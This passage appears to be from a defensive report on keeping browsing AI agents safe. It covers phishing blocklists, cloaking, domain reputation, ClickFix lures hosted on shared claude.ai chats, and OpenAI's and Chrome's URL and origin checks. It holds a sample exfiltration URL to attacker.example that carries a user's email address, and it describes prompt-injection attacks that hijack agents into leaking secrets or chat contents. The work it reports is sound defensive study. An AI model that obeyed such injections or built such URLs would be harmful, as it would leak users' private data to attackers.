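LayerX compared ordinary browsers with AI browsers, which have a built-in agent. It took the 100 most recent phishing pages reported on public sites such as OpenPhish and PhishTank and checked which ones each browser blocked:

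| Browser | Pages blocked |
|---|---|
| Microsoft Edge | 54% |
| Google Chrome | 47% |
| Dia | 46% |
| Perplexity's Comet | 7% |
| Genspark | 7% |

LayerX sells a competing browser add-on, which it says detects 98% of such attacks, so it benefits if browsers look weak. The test used only 100 pages, so Chrome's true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 37% to 57%, and its difference from Edge could be chance. The test is undated, and the products may have changed since.

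However, chance cannot explain the results for Comet and Genspark. All five browsers use Google's open-source Chromium code, but that does not guarantee that they use Google's list. Comet and Genspark stopped the few pages they did because of connection errors such as faulty certificates. Neither browser ever displayed a Safe Browsing warning, although Comet's settings showed Safe Browsing as turned on. Developers should therefore test the browser their agent drives, using Google's harmless test pages, which are meant to trigger the warning.

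### Honest sites on the list

It is harder to measure how often Google lists a safe site, because researchers would have to show that the listed sites were safe. Google warns customers that its lists may contain safe sites.

In October 2025, Google added immich.cloud, a domain belonging to the developers of the photo-storage program Immich, to its list of dangerous sites. The developers believed Google's systems had mistaken test copies of their software for phishing. The warning covered every site under the domain, including ones unrelated to the tests.

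Sites can also stay on a blocklist after they stop being dangerous. After their last experiment, Oest and colleagues replaced all their test pages with error messages and tracked when the blocklists dropped them. The earliest removal came 29 days after the original report. An owner who has cleaned up a hacked site can ask Google for a review, but until Google acts, agents that consult the list will refuse to open the site.

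An agent should still stop at a listed page, since wrong entries seem to be much rarer than correct ones. It should tell the user that Google has listed the site, which is true even if the entry is a mistake.

### Cloaking against scanners

Criminals can keep a page off the list by hiding it from Google's crawlers through cloaking, which means serving different pages to different visitors. For example, a phishing site might check each visitor's IP address, return "404 Not Found" to a security company, and show everyone else a fake bank login.

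*An Analysis of Architectural and Operational Dynamics of Phishkits in the Wild* (Ousat, Tofighi and colleagues, 2026) examined the code of 1,300 phishing kits from 2020 to 2023. A phishing kit is a ready-made package for setting up a fake site. Of these kits, 46% blocked lists of IP addresses belonging to search engines, security companies and similar organisations. Some blocked visitors whose internet provider's name contained a word such as "University". Only 22% used no evasion techniques.

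Much of what phishing kits do to hide from scanners is crude. Ousat and colleagues found 126 kits with the same list of blocked IP addresses, and a scanner can avoid such lists by using an ordinary home internet connection. Pages that require some action from the visitor are harder to scan. In the 2019 tests, Google listed none of the pages that revealed their phishing content only after a mouse movement, a click or a CAPTCHA.

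Cloaking can also mislead an agent that a user has asked to check a suspicious link. If the agent fetches the page from a data centre whose addresses the kit blocks, it may receive an error or a harmless page. The agent may then report that the link looks fine, and the user may open it at home and see the fake login page.

### Pages that only agents receive

A site can also send agents a page containing a prompt injection while sending people and security scanners a normal one. Many agents identify themselves in their requests, and the site can recognise others by their network addresses or browser settings. A user who opens the link to check it will find nothing wrong, and Google will have no reason to list the site because its crawler also gets the normal page.

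In *A Whole New World*, Zychlinski (2025) describes a private test site that showed software documentation to people but showed a coding agent a page that required a secret key from the user's computer before it would display the documentation. The attack worked with 2025 models from Anthropic, OpenAI and Google. Zychlinski tested only one coding program and did not report the number of attempts, so the experiment does not show how often the attack would succeed.

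Chen, Chen and Karray (2026), in *Agent-Targeted Cloaking on the Web*, looked for such differences on 4,705 popular sites in October 2026. They requested the same pages under different names, including Chrome and ChatGPT-User, the name ChatGPT uses when it opens a page for a user. Pages often change between visits because of new headlines or advertisements, so the researchers also fetched each page several times as Chrome to measure normal variation.

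Most of the differences were refusals. Sites refused ChatGPT-User 21% of the time and served it an altered page 4.6% of the time, but an unknown bot also received altered pages on 2.9% of sites. After checking by hand, the researchers found only four sites where text addressed to AI systems was missing from the browser's copy. On three of them, the text concerned documentation. The fourth was a major news publisher, which sent AI agents a bank's sponsored text that neither human readers nor Google's search crawler received.

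Agent-only content therefore seems to be rare on popular sites. This is weak evidence about sites that criminals set up to attack agents, which are unlikely to be among the most visited.

Chen and colleagues suggest that AI search services fetch each page a second time as an ordinary browser and flag any text that appears only in the agent's copy. A simple comparison would raise many false alarms, since normal changes alone made 7.2% of sites look different. The second request should also come from a different network, because a site may recognise the agent by its IP address.

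Agents could also defend themselves by disguise. Zychlinski recommends varying their browser settings so that sites cannot pick them out. Disguise could also get agents past many refusals. When Chen and colleagues ran a program from a university network, 61% of the refusals it met disappeared once it claimed to be Chrome. But honest sites would find it harder to tell disguised agents from unwanted bots. Chen and colleagues instead favour signed requests that prove an agent's identity, which would help honest agents gain access but also make them easier to target.

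### What an agent can query directly

An agent without a browser can check addresses against Google's lists through two services. Safe Browsing is free for non-commercial use only. The *safebrowsing/v5 library* page directs anyone who checks addresses "for sale or revenue-generating purposes" to Web Risk, Google's paid service.

| Service | Price | Age of the data | What Google receives |
|---|---|---|---|
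| Safe Browsing, real-time | Free, non-commercial | Current | Hash prefixes for most unfamiliar pages |
| Safe Browsing, local list | Free, non-commercial | As old as the last download | Prefixes after a local match |
| Web Risk Lookup | 100,000 free calls a month, then $0.50 per 1,000 | Current | The full address |
| Web Risk Update | Free download, then $50 per 1,000 prefix queries | As old as the last download | Prefixes after a local match |

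Web Risk Lookup is the easiest commercial option, but it sends Google every address the agent checks, including any private data in the parameters. The Update service is more private, and it charges more per query but needs few queries. For an agent service that opens a million pages a month, Lookup would cost $450. Update would cost about $370 for about 7,500 queries, based on the earlier estimate of false matches on 0.75% of pages. However, Update may miss a new scam until the next download.

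A non-commercial agent in a short-lived container can use Google's *No Storage Real Time Mode* without first downloading a list. The client sends prefixes for every page unless it has a recent answer. Google also offers a version that hides the agent's IP address by using a relay, but its documentation, *Safe Browsing Oblivious HTTP Gateway API*, is unfinished. Under the terms summarised in Google's *Overview*, programs that warn users must follow Google's wording and credit Google, so a developer should not let the model write the warning.

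Other lists can fill some gaps. The Russian company Yandex offers a list with a similar prefix system, described in its *URL and hashing*. But some public lists are very slow to add domains. *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration (2025)* compared several with the feed of the Anti-Phishing Working Group, an industry association. Phishing.Database listed the same domains a median of 64 days later, and Phishunt more than two years later.

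Even a large collection of lists misses some dangerous sites. *PhishLumos (2025)* describes a system that found 77,391 suspected phishing addresses by looking for links between known phishing sites. Nearly 20% of them were not flagged by any of the 90 security engines on VirusTotal, a service that combines results from many companies. Some of those addresses may have been harmless, since no engine confirmed them.

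Whichever list a developer chooses, ordinary code outside the model should query it before the agent opens a page and again after every redirect.

### Why "not listed" does not mean "safe"

Google's real-time check returns SAFE when it finds no match, which only means that the address is not on the list. Suppose that 100 out of 10,000 online shops are fraudulent. If Chrome blocked them at the initial rate for shopping scams in Kaur and colleagues' study, it would block 12 or 13. If the agent then picked one of the remaining shops at random, it would have a 0.88% chance of picking a fraudulent one, compared with 1% before the check.

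A fake Walmart shop in a later case was not on the list either. An agent that treats SAFE as approval may skip other checks or pay without asking the user. To prevent this, the code that queries Google can pass the model a message such as "no entry found" instead of SAFE. The developer can also require the user's approval for any payment to an unfamiliar shop, regardless of the lookup result.

A slower investigation can catch much of what the list misses. Kaur and colleagues' AI system clicks through a site, fills in forms with invented details and searches for outside evidence about the company. In a test, it missed 31 of 1,551 scams and wrongly flagged 47 of 1,500 legitimate sites. It took a median of 44 seconds per site, which may be acceptable before a purchase but not before every page. Like any model that reads a suspicious page, the system is also exposed to prompt injection.

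A list can still help after a payment. Chrome blocked 12.5% of the shopping scams at first but 26.7% within a week. An agent could keep a record of the shops it has paid, check them again a week later, and tell the user to contact the bank if one has since appeared on the list.

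## Domain reputation, and harmful pages on trusted domains

A blocklist can include a site only after someone has found it. Reputation systems are meant to assess a domain earlier, using evidence such as its age, its registrar and the other sites on the same server. The best of them work well against domains that criminals register themselves. They fail when someone other than the owner puts a harmful page on a reputable domain, which happened repeatedly in 2026 on claude.ai, the website of Anthropic's AI assistant.

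### What goes into a score

Most of the evidence comes from outside the page. Registration records show when someone registered the domain and which company, called the registrar, sold it. Passive DNS is a database of name lookups observed by sensors near DNS servers. It shows which IP addresses a domain has used and how often people looked it up. Popularity lists rank domains by traffic.

| Evidence | What raises suspicion | Honest sites that match |
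|---|---|---|
| Domain age | Registered days ago | Every new business |
| Registrar and ending | Cheap, with much past abuse | Anyone who wanted a cheap name |
| Name servers and time of registration | Many similar names registered together | A company protecting its brand |
| Shared hosting | Malicious neighbours on the same IP address | Customers of any large host |
| Query pattern | Few lookups, or a short burst | A site for a festival |
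| Past abuse | Earlier entries on blocklists | A hacked site that its owner has repaired |
| Popularity rank | Missing from the lists | Most small sites |

No row in the table is strong evidence on its own. For example, Interisle (2026), a consultancy that studies domain abuse, found that blocklists had flagged 34.6% of the .top domains registered in 2025 and 4.9% of the .com domains. But .com is so large that it still had more flagged domains in total.

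Shared hosting can mislead even more. *A Longitudinal Study of Recently Observed Malicious Domains* (Mashood and Nabeel, 2026) examined 1.52 million domains that at least five VirusTotal engines had flagged. Two IP addresses each served more than 230,000 of the domains that attackers had apparently registered. Such addresses mostly belong to Cloudflare, which also proxies many legitimate sites, so blocking the addresses would cut off those sites too.

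### How MANTIS scores a domain

Researchers have combined these signals since at least 2010, when a system called Notos scored domains using passive DNS data. *PREDATOR* later used only information available when a domain was registered. It caught 70% of malicious .com and .net domains and wrongly flagged 0.35% of the others.

A more recent system, described by Deniz, Nabeel and colleagues (2025), in *MANTIS*, starts from the observation that criminals reuse servers. More than 80% of the IP addresses that hosted malicious domains on a given day had also done so in the previous week. MANTIS builds a new blocklist every day:

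1. **Seeds.** It collects about 3,000 domains that VirusTotal has just seen for the first time, that several scanners flag, and that criminals probably registered themselves.
2. **Neighbours.** From passive DNS it takes the seeds' IP addresses, then up to 200 domains that recently used each address, then the other addresses of those domains.
3. **Features.** It describes each name (length, suspicious words, character patterns), its hosting (name servers, number of addresses, frequency of lookups) and each IP address (how many domains share it, and for how long it has appeared in the records).
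4. **Labels.** The malicious examples are seeds and neighbours that scanners had already flagged. Of the honest examples, 54% come from popularity lists and 5% are educational or government sites. The other 41% are mostly obscure domains that passed several filters and that no scanner flagged.
5. **Training.** A neural network combines each domain's features with those of its neighbours, three times over, and learns which combinations go with the malicious label.

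The features are essential because most neighbours of malicious domains are benign. Around addresses that had hosted malicious domains, 6.3% of domains were malicious, compared with 0.2% in general. When Deniz and colleagues removed the features and kept only the network of connections, their models wrongly flagged between 12.8% and 21.1% of benign domains.

With everything included, MANTIS caught 86.9% of malicious domains at a setting that wrongly flagged 0.1% of honest ones. A looser setting caught 95.6% and wrongly flagged 0.5%. At the strict setting, 99.7% of the flagged domains were malicious, but so were about three in ten of all the domains in the tests. The result would look different in ordinary browsing. Applying the same rates to 100,000 domains gives:

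| Population | Setting | Malicious domains caught | Honest domains flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| All domains, 0.2% malicious | Strict | 174 of 200 | 100 |
| All domains, 0.2% malicious | Loose | 191 of 200 | 499 |
| New domains, 10% malicious | Strict | 8,690 of 10,000 | 90 |
| New domains, 10% malicious | Loose | 9,560 of 10,000 | 450 |

Across all domains, more than a third of the strict setting's alarms would be false. The real share is probably higher, because Deniz and colleagues excluded obscure domains with invalid certificates or brand-like names from their honest examples, and a detector is especially likely to flag honest sites of that kind.

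MANTIS also deliberately excludes legitimate domains that attackers have taken over, which made up about 18% of the blocklisted domains the researchers analysed. It excludes hosting services such as weebly.com and blogspot.com too, where customers publish under the host's domain. Çolhak, Demirkıran and colleagues (2026), in *PhiShark2026*, made 33,387 scans of live phishing pages between April and August 2026, and 45% of those pages were on free hosting.

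### What it costs to distrust new domains

Instead of scoring new domains, some security companies advise customers to block them all. CircleID's *The Latest DNS Threat Landscape* recommends this even before anyone has classified a domain as malicious. The advice makes economic sense because criminals use up domains quickly and buy new ones, very rarely renewing the old. Interisle also cites research in which each dollar off the price was associated with a 49% increase in malicious registrations.

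Estimates of the share of domains that are malicious range from under 1% to 25%, depending on what the researchers count. Interisle counted 84,961,989 domains registered in 2025 under generic endings such as .com and .shop, not country endings such as .be. By 18 May 2026, 10% of them were on blocklists. Interisle projects that criminals bought about 20%, after allowing for domains that will be discovered later and unlisted domains bought in bulk with listed ones. Infoblox's *2025 DNS Threat Landscape Report* (2025) puts the share at 25% of newly observed domains, but that figure includes domains that are only "suspicious", and Infoblox sells filtering.

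In the certificate-log study by Kaur and colleagues, 0.7% of working websites were confirmed scams, the lowest of these figures. Only about 2.5% of the domains they checked had a working website, so the 0.7% figure leaves out domains that criminals use only to send spam or control malware. It is still the closest of these figures to what an agent encounters when it opens a new site.

An agent that refused every domain less than 30 days old would block about seven million generic domains at any moment, at the 2025 registration rate. About 6.3 million of them would be honest if Interisle's 10% figure for malicious domains is right, or 5.6 million if the true share is 20%. Over the year, the rule would block 76.6 million honest domains for a month each, or about nine for every domain known to be malicious. Many of the honest domains have no website yet, so nobody would notice. Among working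 sites, however, Kaur and colleagues' figures imply 136 honest sites for each scam.

The rule would also miss most attacks. In Mashood and Nabeel's data, the median attack domain was 60 days old when VirusTotal first recorded it, and only 29.9% were detected within a week of registration. To catch 90% of them, the rule would have to cover domains up to 13 months old. Even that figure is optimistic, because Mashood and Nabeel assume that any flagged domain more than three years old is a hacked legitimate site.

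Domain age helps distinguish phishing sites from legitimate ones when the domain is very new or very old. Çolhak and colleagues found that 21.0% of phishing domains outside free hosting were at most a week old, while 91.5% of legitimate domains were more than five years old. However, they drew the legitimate domains from a list of ten million well-linked domains, which favours old sites.

### Malicious instructions on claude.ai

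From 8 April 2026, people who searched Google for AI programming tools saw advertisements for fake download pages. Trend Micro's *Threat Actors Abuse claude.ai Shared Chat for ClickFix Malvertising Campaign* traces the operation through about 2,500 recorded visits. At first the attackers used free sites on GitLab Pages, such as claude-code-app.gitlab.io, and kept replacing them. Trend Micro counted 92 such names. On 6 May the attackers began moving to claude.ai itself, which lets users publish a conversation at a public address:

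1. The attacker published a conversation made to look like a guide from "Apple Support".
2. A Google advertisement led straight to it.
3. The guide told visitors to open the Mac's Terminal program and paste in a command. The command was encoded, which hid the address inside it.
4. The command downloaded a script from another domain. The script installed MacSync, which steals browser passwords, login cookies, SSH keys and cryptocurrency wallets.

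From 21 May, every visit Trend Micro observed went to claude.ai. Anthropic banned the accounts and disabled the conversations after Trend Micro reported them.

| Address | Whom the domain's reputation describes | Who wrote the content |
|---|---|---|
| claude-code-app.gitlab.io | GitLab, unless the software separates its customers | The attacker |
| claude.ai/share/… | Anthropic | The attacker |
| The domain in the hidden command | Whoever controls that domain | The attacker |

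When a stranger writes a page on claude.ai, the certificate is valid, the domain name is the intended one and the operator, Anthropic, is honest. A reputation check on the domain gives a correct answer about Anthropic but does not assess the stranger who wrote the page.

The GitLab pages were easier to tell apart from their host. Because gitlab.io is on the Public Suffix List, software can treat each customer's subdomain as a separate site and detect that it is new. A shared conversation differs from the rest of claude.ai only in its path, which does not appear in certificates, DNS records or registration data. A blocklist can include a single path, but the attackers used at least 61 different conversations in the last wave alone.

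Other attackers did the same on several services. In December 2025 the security company Huntress described shared ChatGPT and Grok conversations that told Mac users to paste a command to free disk space. The command installed a password stealer. A 2026 warning from Azerbaijan's national cyber-security team, *Malware campaign abusing ChatGPT shared links detected*, describes pages on chatgpt.com that announced a false outage and offered malware disguised as the ChatGPT desktop app.

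Claude's artifacts, small documents or programs that users can publish, had the same weakness. Two artifacts with false instructions for installing Homebrew, a Mac tool for installing software, received about 25,000 clicks, according to AdGuard's *Claude-linked Google ads dupe macOS users into installing malware*. In July 2026 another artifact posed as the download page for Claude's desktop program. IT Security Guru's *FakeAgent Campaign* (2026) reports that the page, advertised on Bing with a link to the real claude.ai, compromised at least 29 organisations in two days.

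These reports describe human victims, but a coding agent could be easier to fool. If a user asks it to install Claude's desktop program, it may find such a page by searching, and a developer who permits only trusted domains may well have included claude.ai. An agent with terminal access could then run the command itself.

Refusing everything on shared hosts would also block legitimate software. Homebrew's genuine instructions also involve pasting a command that downloads a script from raw.githubusercontent.com, where any GitHub user can store files. The path there begins with the account name, so ordinary code can check that the account is Homebrew's. The path of a shared Claude conversation is a random identifier that contains no information about the author. An agent should therefore treat a shared conversation as text from an unknown person, whatever the domain's score.

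A second check is possible when the command runs. The encoding hides the download address from a person or model reading the page, but the computer still has to connect to that address. A proxy that checks every domain the agent contacts would see the attacker's domain.

### Old domains under new control

Attackers can also gain a good reputation by waiting. Interisle reports that some criminals leave domains unused for months because scoring systems distrust young ones. Between June and December 2025, blocklists added 2.32 million domains registered in 2024, all at least five months old when listed. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, acknowledges that its detector for new registrations misses such domains. Unit 42 also watches passive DNS for old domains that start carrying malicious traffic.

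An attacker can buy an old domain instead of waiting for a new one to age. If an owner stops paying for a domain, it eventually becomes available, and whoever registers it next can inherit the old site's links and visitors. This resets the creation date, so an age check would show that the registration is new. But registrars auction many expired domains before they become available, and a domain sold this way keeps its original creation date.

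An attacker may not need to own the domain. Suppose a company points files.example.com to storage it rents from a cloud provider, then cancels the storage but forgets to delete the DNS record. If the provider lets customers choose their own storage names, an attacker can rent storage under the abandoned name, and files.example.com will then show the attacker's pages. The attacker can also obtain a valid certificate, because the CA's request for the test file reaches the attacker's storage.

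In February 2025, a group that Infoblox calls Hazy Hawk used forgotten records of this kind to take over several subdomains of the US Centers for Disease Control and Prevention, while the parent domain, cdc.gov, kept its excellent reputation.

Hacked sites also stay undetected longer. *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration* reports a median time to detection of 86 days for compromised phishing domains and 16.3 days for domains that criminals had registered themselves.

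### What an agent can look up

**Registration data.** The Registration Data Access Protocol (RDAP), the successor to WHOIS, returns a domain's registration record in machine-readable form. An agent can query it free of charge for the registrar, the name servers and the dates of registration and expiry. ICANN, which oversees generic domain endings, requires their registrars and registries to provide this service. Registries for country endings often publish less data or none. Çolhak and colleagues obtained a usable creation date for only about 75% of scans of phishing pages outside free hosting and 80% of scans of legitimate pages, so a missing date is weak evidence either way.

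Raskar, Chari and colleagues (2025) observe in *Upgrade or Switch* that since the GDPR, the EU's data protection law, most domain registration records hide the owner's name and contact details by redaction or behind a proxy service. The remaining information is largely supplied by the registrant and unchecked. *LOKI* (2025), a system for finding scam sites, still uses a hidden registrant and a free email address as features, but these signals are now weaker because most honest owners are hidden too and an agent can seldom see the email address.

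Tranco publishes a free popularity ranking of a million domains, and Google's Chrome User Experience Report groups sites into broad popularity bands. A high rank suggests that a domain isn't a throwaway, but doesn't prove that it is trustworthy. Mashood and Nabeel found 4,422 domains in Tranco's top 500,000 that at least five security engines had flagged within five months, though some may be false alarms. Deniz and colleagues accepted a domain from the daily lists only if it had stayed there for 30 days, because attackers' domains tend to be popular only briefly.

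**DNS records.** An agent can also check whether a domain is set up to receive email. Çolhak and colleagues found mail records for 86.7% of legitimate domains and 29.7% of phishing domains outside free hosting. An attacker can add such a record in a minute, so the check would become less useful if many agents relied on it.

**Commercial scores.** Companies such as Infoblox and Spamhaus sell domain reputation scores based on far more DNS traffic than an agent could collect. Spamhaus' *Domain Reputation Updates* reports 3.37 million malicious and suspicious listings for April to September 2026, up 56.6%. Customers usually cannot see how the company reached a score, which makes it hard to explain to the user or the site's owner why an agent refused to use the site.

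Attackers can improve all of these signals, often for little money. A .com name costs a little more than a .top name and looks better. A site that uses Cloudflare shares servers with respectable sites. Automated visits or lookups can push a domain up some popularity lists, and a page on a trusted host is free. A score therefore works best against criminals who need thousands of domains, since they pay the extra cost for each one. It works less well against someone who wants to defraud a single company and can afford to pay that cost once.

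### Asking the user instead of blocking

The main objection to using reputation is that it favors large, old sites. A new bakery's site has a young domain, no rank and perhaps a cheap host, as a fake shop's does. If agents avoid it, it will not get the visitors it needs to build a reputation. The usual reply is that an agent can treat a low score as a reason to ask the user rather than to block the site.

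The registry for Belgium's .be domains already uses a score this way. Its RegCheck system, developed with the Dutch registry, scores each new registration. If the score is suspicious, the buyer keeps the name but must prove their identity before the domain works. According to DNS Belgium's *Blocking suspicious domains before they go live* (2025), flagging about 30% of registrations finds about 80% of the fraudulent ones. At that setting, about 62,000 of the nearly 208,000 names registered in 2025 would need an identity check. In the seven months after RegCheck launched in March 2024, malicious registrations fell by 30% from the same months a year earlier, though other causes may have contributed.

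A score like RegCheck's can also reinforce its own mistakes. DNS Belgium's *be Registrant verification now also with Machine Learning* (2024) explains that the training examples of bad registrations include names whose buyers never completed the identity check. Some of those buyers may have been honest people who gave up, and training on their registrations makes the next version of the model more likely to flag similar buyers.

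Unlike a registry, an agent's user cannot demand an identity document from a shop. If the agent asked about every new site, the user would, going by Kaur and colleagues' ratio, approve about 136 honest ones for each scam, and would probably stop reading the question. The agent should ask only when the site is unfamiliar and the next step could do real harm, such as paying, entering a password or running a downloaded program. It should also give the user a fact to act on, for example that the shop's domain is nine days old.

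With those limits, the reply to the objection is mostly convincing. The bakery's customers can read its opening hours without interruption and confirm once, on their first order. The agent would still treat the bakery unfairly if it chose between shops on its own and quietly preferred one that needed no confirmation. To avoid this, a developer can keep the score out of the ranking and use it only at payment. A high score should not remove the need for confirmation either, since the harmful pages on claude.ai would have passed the reputation check.

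## OpenAI's and Chrome's checks against known public addresses

Blocklists and reputation scores help an agent decide whether a site is safe to visit. But opening a page also sends its address to the site, and an attacker can trick an agent into putting the user's private data in that address. OpenAI explained in January 2026 that ChatGPT limits this risk by opening an address automatically only if a crawler has already found that exact address on the public web. Google had announced a similar restriction for Chrome's agent in December 2025, as part of a larger design.

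### How an address can leak private data

Suppose Anna asks an agent to compare hotels, and the conversation contains her email address. One of the hotel pages hides a prompt injection that tells the agent to open this address:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=anna%40example.org`

The `%40` stands for the @ sign. Web servers commonly log the addresses that visitors request, so the attacker only has to read the log. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that the user may not notice, because an agent can request an address in the background, for instance to load an image.

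Models are trained to refuse such instructions, but they don't do so reliably. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a 2025 attack, hidden in an ordinary-looking work email, that succeeded in half of the tests. Also in 2025, Gemini's browsing tool could send an attacker the user's saved information and location. According to Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool*, Google's defences against leaks through images did not apply to browsing, and Google has since fixed the flaw. According to Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Gemini also checked links against Safe Browsing, but this list is unlikely to include a domain that an attacker has just registered.

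### How OpenAI's check works

OpenAI's method doesn't depend on recognising the attacker or the injection:

1. A crawler visits public pages and records the addresses it finds, much as a search engine does. It has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When the agent is about to fetch an address automatically, the system looks for exactly that address in the crawler's records.
3. If the address is there, the agent opens it.
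4. If not, the system either tells the agent to try a different site or shows the user a warning. The warning displays the address and explains that it may contain information from the conversation.

The crawler knows nothing about Anna, so an address it has recorded is unlikely to contain her data. Four addresses illustrate the result:

| Address the agent wants to open | In the index? | Result |
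|---|---|---|
| `https://shop.example.com/returns` | Yes, the shop's home page links to it | Opens |
| `https://attacker.example/collect?data=anna%40example.org` | No | Refused or shown to Anna |
| `https://shop.example.com/go?to=attacker.example/anna` | No | Refused or shown to Anna |
| `https://shop.example.com/orders/view?id=42` | No, it appears only in Anna's order email | Refused or shown to Anna, although it is harmless |

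Exact matching is difficult because one address can have several spellings. In an example from text/plain's *Guidelines for URL Storage and Comparison* (2026), the Korean syllable 자 becomes `%EC%9E%90` in a path, and not all programs follow the standard encoding. A strict comparison may therefore reject a public page because its address is spelled differently. A comparison that accepts different spellings can leak a small amount of information, because the three letters in `%EC%9E%90` can each be upper or lower case without changing the meaning, and a server could record which of the eight spellings the agent used. A developer can avoid both problems by allowing for different spellings in the comparison and then fetching the address as the crawler recorded it.

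### Why OpenAI rejected a list of trusted sites

A simpler rule would let the agent open only well-known sites. OpenAI gives two reasons against it.

Many reputable sites have redirects, which send a visitor on to another address. In the table's third row, the shop has a page that forwards visitors to the address in the `to` parameter. A domain-only check would approve the request, and the shop would then pass Anna's name to the attacker. Requiring an exact match prevents this leak because the crawler has never seen that address with Anna's name in it. Criminals already use redirects on trusted domains to make their links look trustworthy. LevelBlue's *Weaponizing Safe Links* describes a phishing email whose link ran through redirects at five security companies.

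A page in the index may redirect elsewhere, but the server choosing the destination does not have the contents of Anna's conversation, so it cannot add her data. It can still send the agent to a dangerous page, so checking a blocklist after every redirect remains useful.

OpenAI's other reason is that people visit far more sites than any short list would contain, so users would see frequent false alarms and learn to click through warnings without reading them. This is a fair criticism of a short list, which would raise false alarms on obscure domains. But OpenAI's exact matching can also raise them, as the order page shows, because it flags personal and new pages on any domain. OpenAI doesn't report in its post how many warnings users see, so it is hard to tell how much better its method is in this respect.

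### What OpenAI guarantees

OpenAI limits its promise to "preventing the agent from quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself" when the agent fetches something. "Quietly" means that data can still leave if the user approves the warning. "Through the URL itself" excludes other routes, such as a form that the agent fills in.

OpenAI also warns that a page that passes the check may still have untrustworthy content or contain misleading or harmful instructions, and the site may try to manipulate the user. A match does not guarantee that browsing is safe in general.

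An agent therefore can't answer any of the four questions about authenticity from a match. A crawler can record a fake ticket shop's address as easily as FIFA's. A genuine download page also keeps the same address when attackers replace the file it offers, as they did at DAEMON Tools.

### Chrome's design of December 2025

Chrome's agent works inside the user's own browser, where the user may be logged in to a bank or an email account. A hijacked agent could read one site and pass the contents to another. Browsers' same-origin policy normally stops a web page from reading content from a different origin. An origin is the combination of scheme, host name and port, so shop.example.com and pay.example.com are separate origins. An agent has to work across origins to be useful, and *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes how Google planned to keep some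 of the separation.

Google calls the central part of Chrome's design Agent Origin Sets. For each task, Chrome keeps one set of origins that the agent may only read and another where it may also click and type. If a user asks the agent to buy the ingredients for a recipe, the recipe site would be in the first set and the grocer's site in the second. The user's bank site would be in neither, so Chrome would not pass its contents to the model. An injection in the recipe could make the agent type data into the grocer's site but not into an attacker's site.

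Opening a read-only page still sends its address, so Chrome also limits addresses written by the model to "known, public URLs". Parker does not explain how Chrome decides which addresses are known.

A separate model, the User Alignment Critic, reviews each action before Chrome carries it out. It receives a description of the action but no unfiltered page content, so a web page cannot give it instructions directly. If the user wants a T-shirt and the agent proposes opening a bank account page, the critic can veto the action.

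| Part of the design | Code or model | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Public-address check | Code | Blocks addresses written by the model unless they are known and public |
| Choice of origins | Model | Judges whether a new origin is relevant to the task |
| Enforcement of the sets | Code | Keeps the agent within the chosen origins |
| User Alignment Critic | Model | Approves or vetoes each action |
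| Sensitive-site list | Code | Makes the agent ask before opening sites such as banks or medical portals |
| Confirmation of purchases and messages | Code and models | Pauses the agent so that the user can approve or finish the step |
| Injection detector | Model | Looks for hostile instructions on each page |

When Parker's post appeared, the agent was still in preview and Google had built only the read-writable set. Google wanted to see how the restrictions affected real tasks before adding the read-only set.

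In the public-address check, code compares any address the model writes with known public addresses. If a page moves the browser to a new origin by itself, the critic judges the move. The critic gives a weaker guarantee because it is a model and can make mistakes that an exact comparison cannot.

None of these parts was meant to recognise a fraudulent shop. Buying a T-shirt from a fake shop matches the user's goal as well as buying one from a real shop, so it should pass the critic's check. The sensitive-site list can include a real bank's address, but not a lookalike domain that a criminal has just registered.

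Chrome's password handling protects better against lookalike sites. The agent must ask the user before signing in through Google Password Manager, and the model has no direct access to stored passwords. A password manager normally offers a password only on the site where the user saved it, so it wouldn't offer the user's bank password on a lookalike of the bank's site.

### What has changed since

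Google released the agent, called auto browse, on 28 January 2026, according to Bloomberg's *Google Chrome’s AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users* (2026). At first, it was available only with Google's more expensive AI subscriptions. Google extended it in December to a cheaper plan in the United States and India, according to McNeal's *Chrome’s auto browse feature is coming to the cheaper AI Plus tier* (2026).

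In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) of the University of Washington tested Chrome and six other browsers with AI features around the time of the launch. They built a page containing a frame from another origin, a form and a prompt injection. The injection contained instructions for the agent to include the frame's contents when the user asked for a summary, and to type the summary into the form, which then automatically sent it to the attacker.

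The full attack worked on ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser, in agent mode. Chrome with Gemini met the preconditions, so a successful injection could have had the same effect there. That would be consistent with Chrome not yet having a read-only set, which is meant to hide unrelated frames from the model. The attack also shows the limits of checking addresses, because it sent the stolen text out through a form.

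In August 2026, *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) again described the critic, the limits on origins and the pauses for approval. The post mentions only one limit, to relevant origins, so it doesn't show whether Google has added the read-only set. That same month, the security company Zenity Labs used hidden instructions to hijack Gemini, Atlas and three other browser agents, as Callahan reported for the news site Forkast.

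Google's engineers have also proposed permissions that the browser would enforce for any agent controlling it through WebDriver BiDi, a protocol for automating browsers. *谷歌拟给浏览器AI加道“权限锁”* (2026), from the Chinese technology site IT之家, gives the example of a user who lets an agent look for products on a shopping site but forbids it to open an outside payment site. The proposal is a prototype, and Google has not decided whether to put it into Chrome. The permissions also do not distinguish between buttons, so an agent allowed to click on a site could still press "Delete".

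OpenAI has extended its check, which it now calls Safe Url. By March 2026, the check covered pages and bookmarks opened in Atlas, as well as searches and page visits in Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that compiles long reports.

OpenAI also offers a stricter option, Lockdown Mode, launched in February 2026, in which ChatGPT can read only saved copies of web pages. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* explains that browsing in this mode sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network, so an attacker's server has nothing to log. The mode also turns off Deep Research and agent mode. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* warns that connected apps may still leak data and that the setting does not affect network access in Codex, the company's coding agent. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports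 that researchers bypassed the mode through a flaw in ChatGPT's preview of HTML files, and that OpenAI has since patched the flaw.

### Attackers who get addresses indexed in advance

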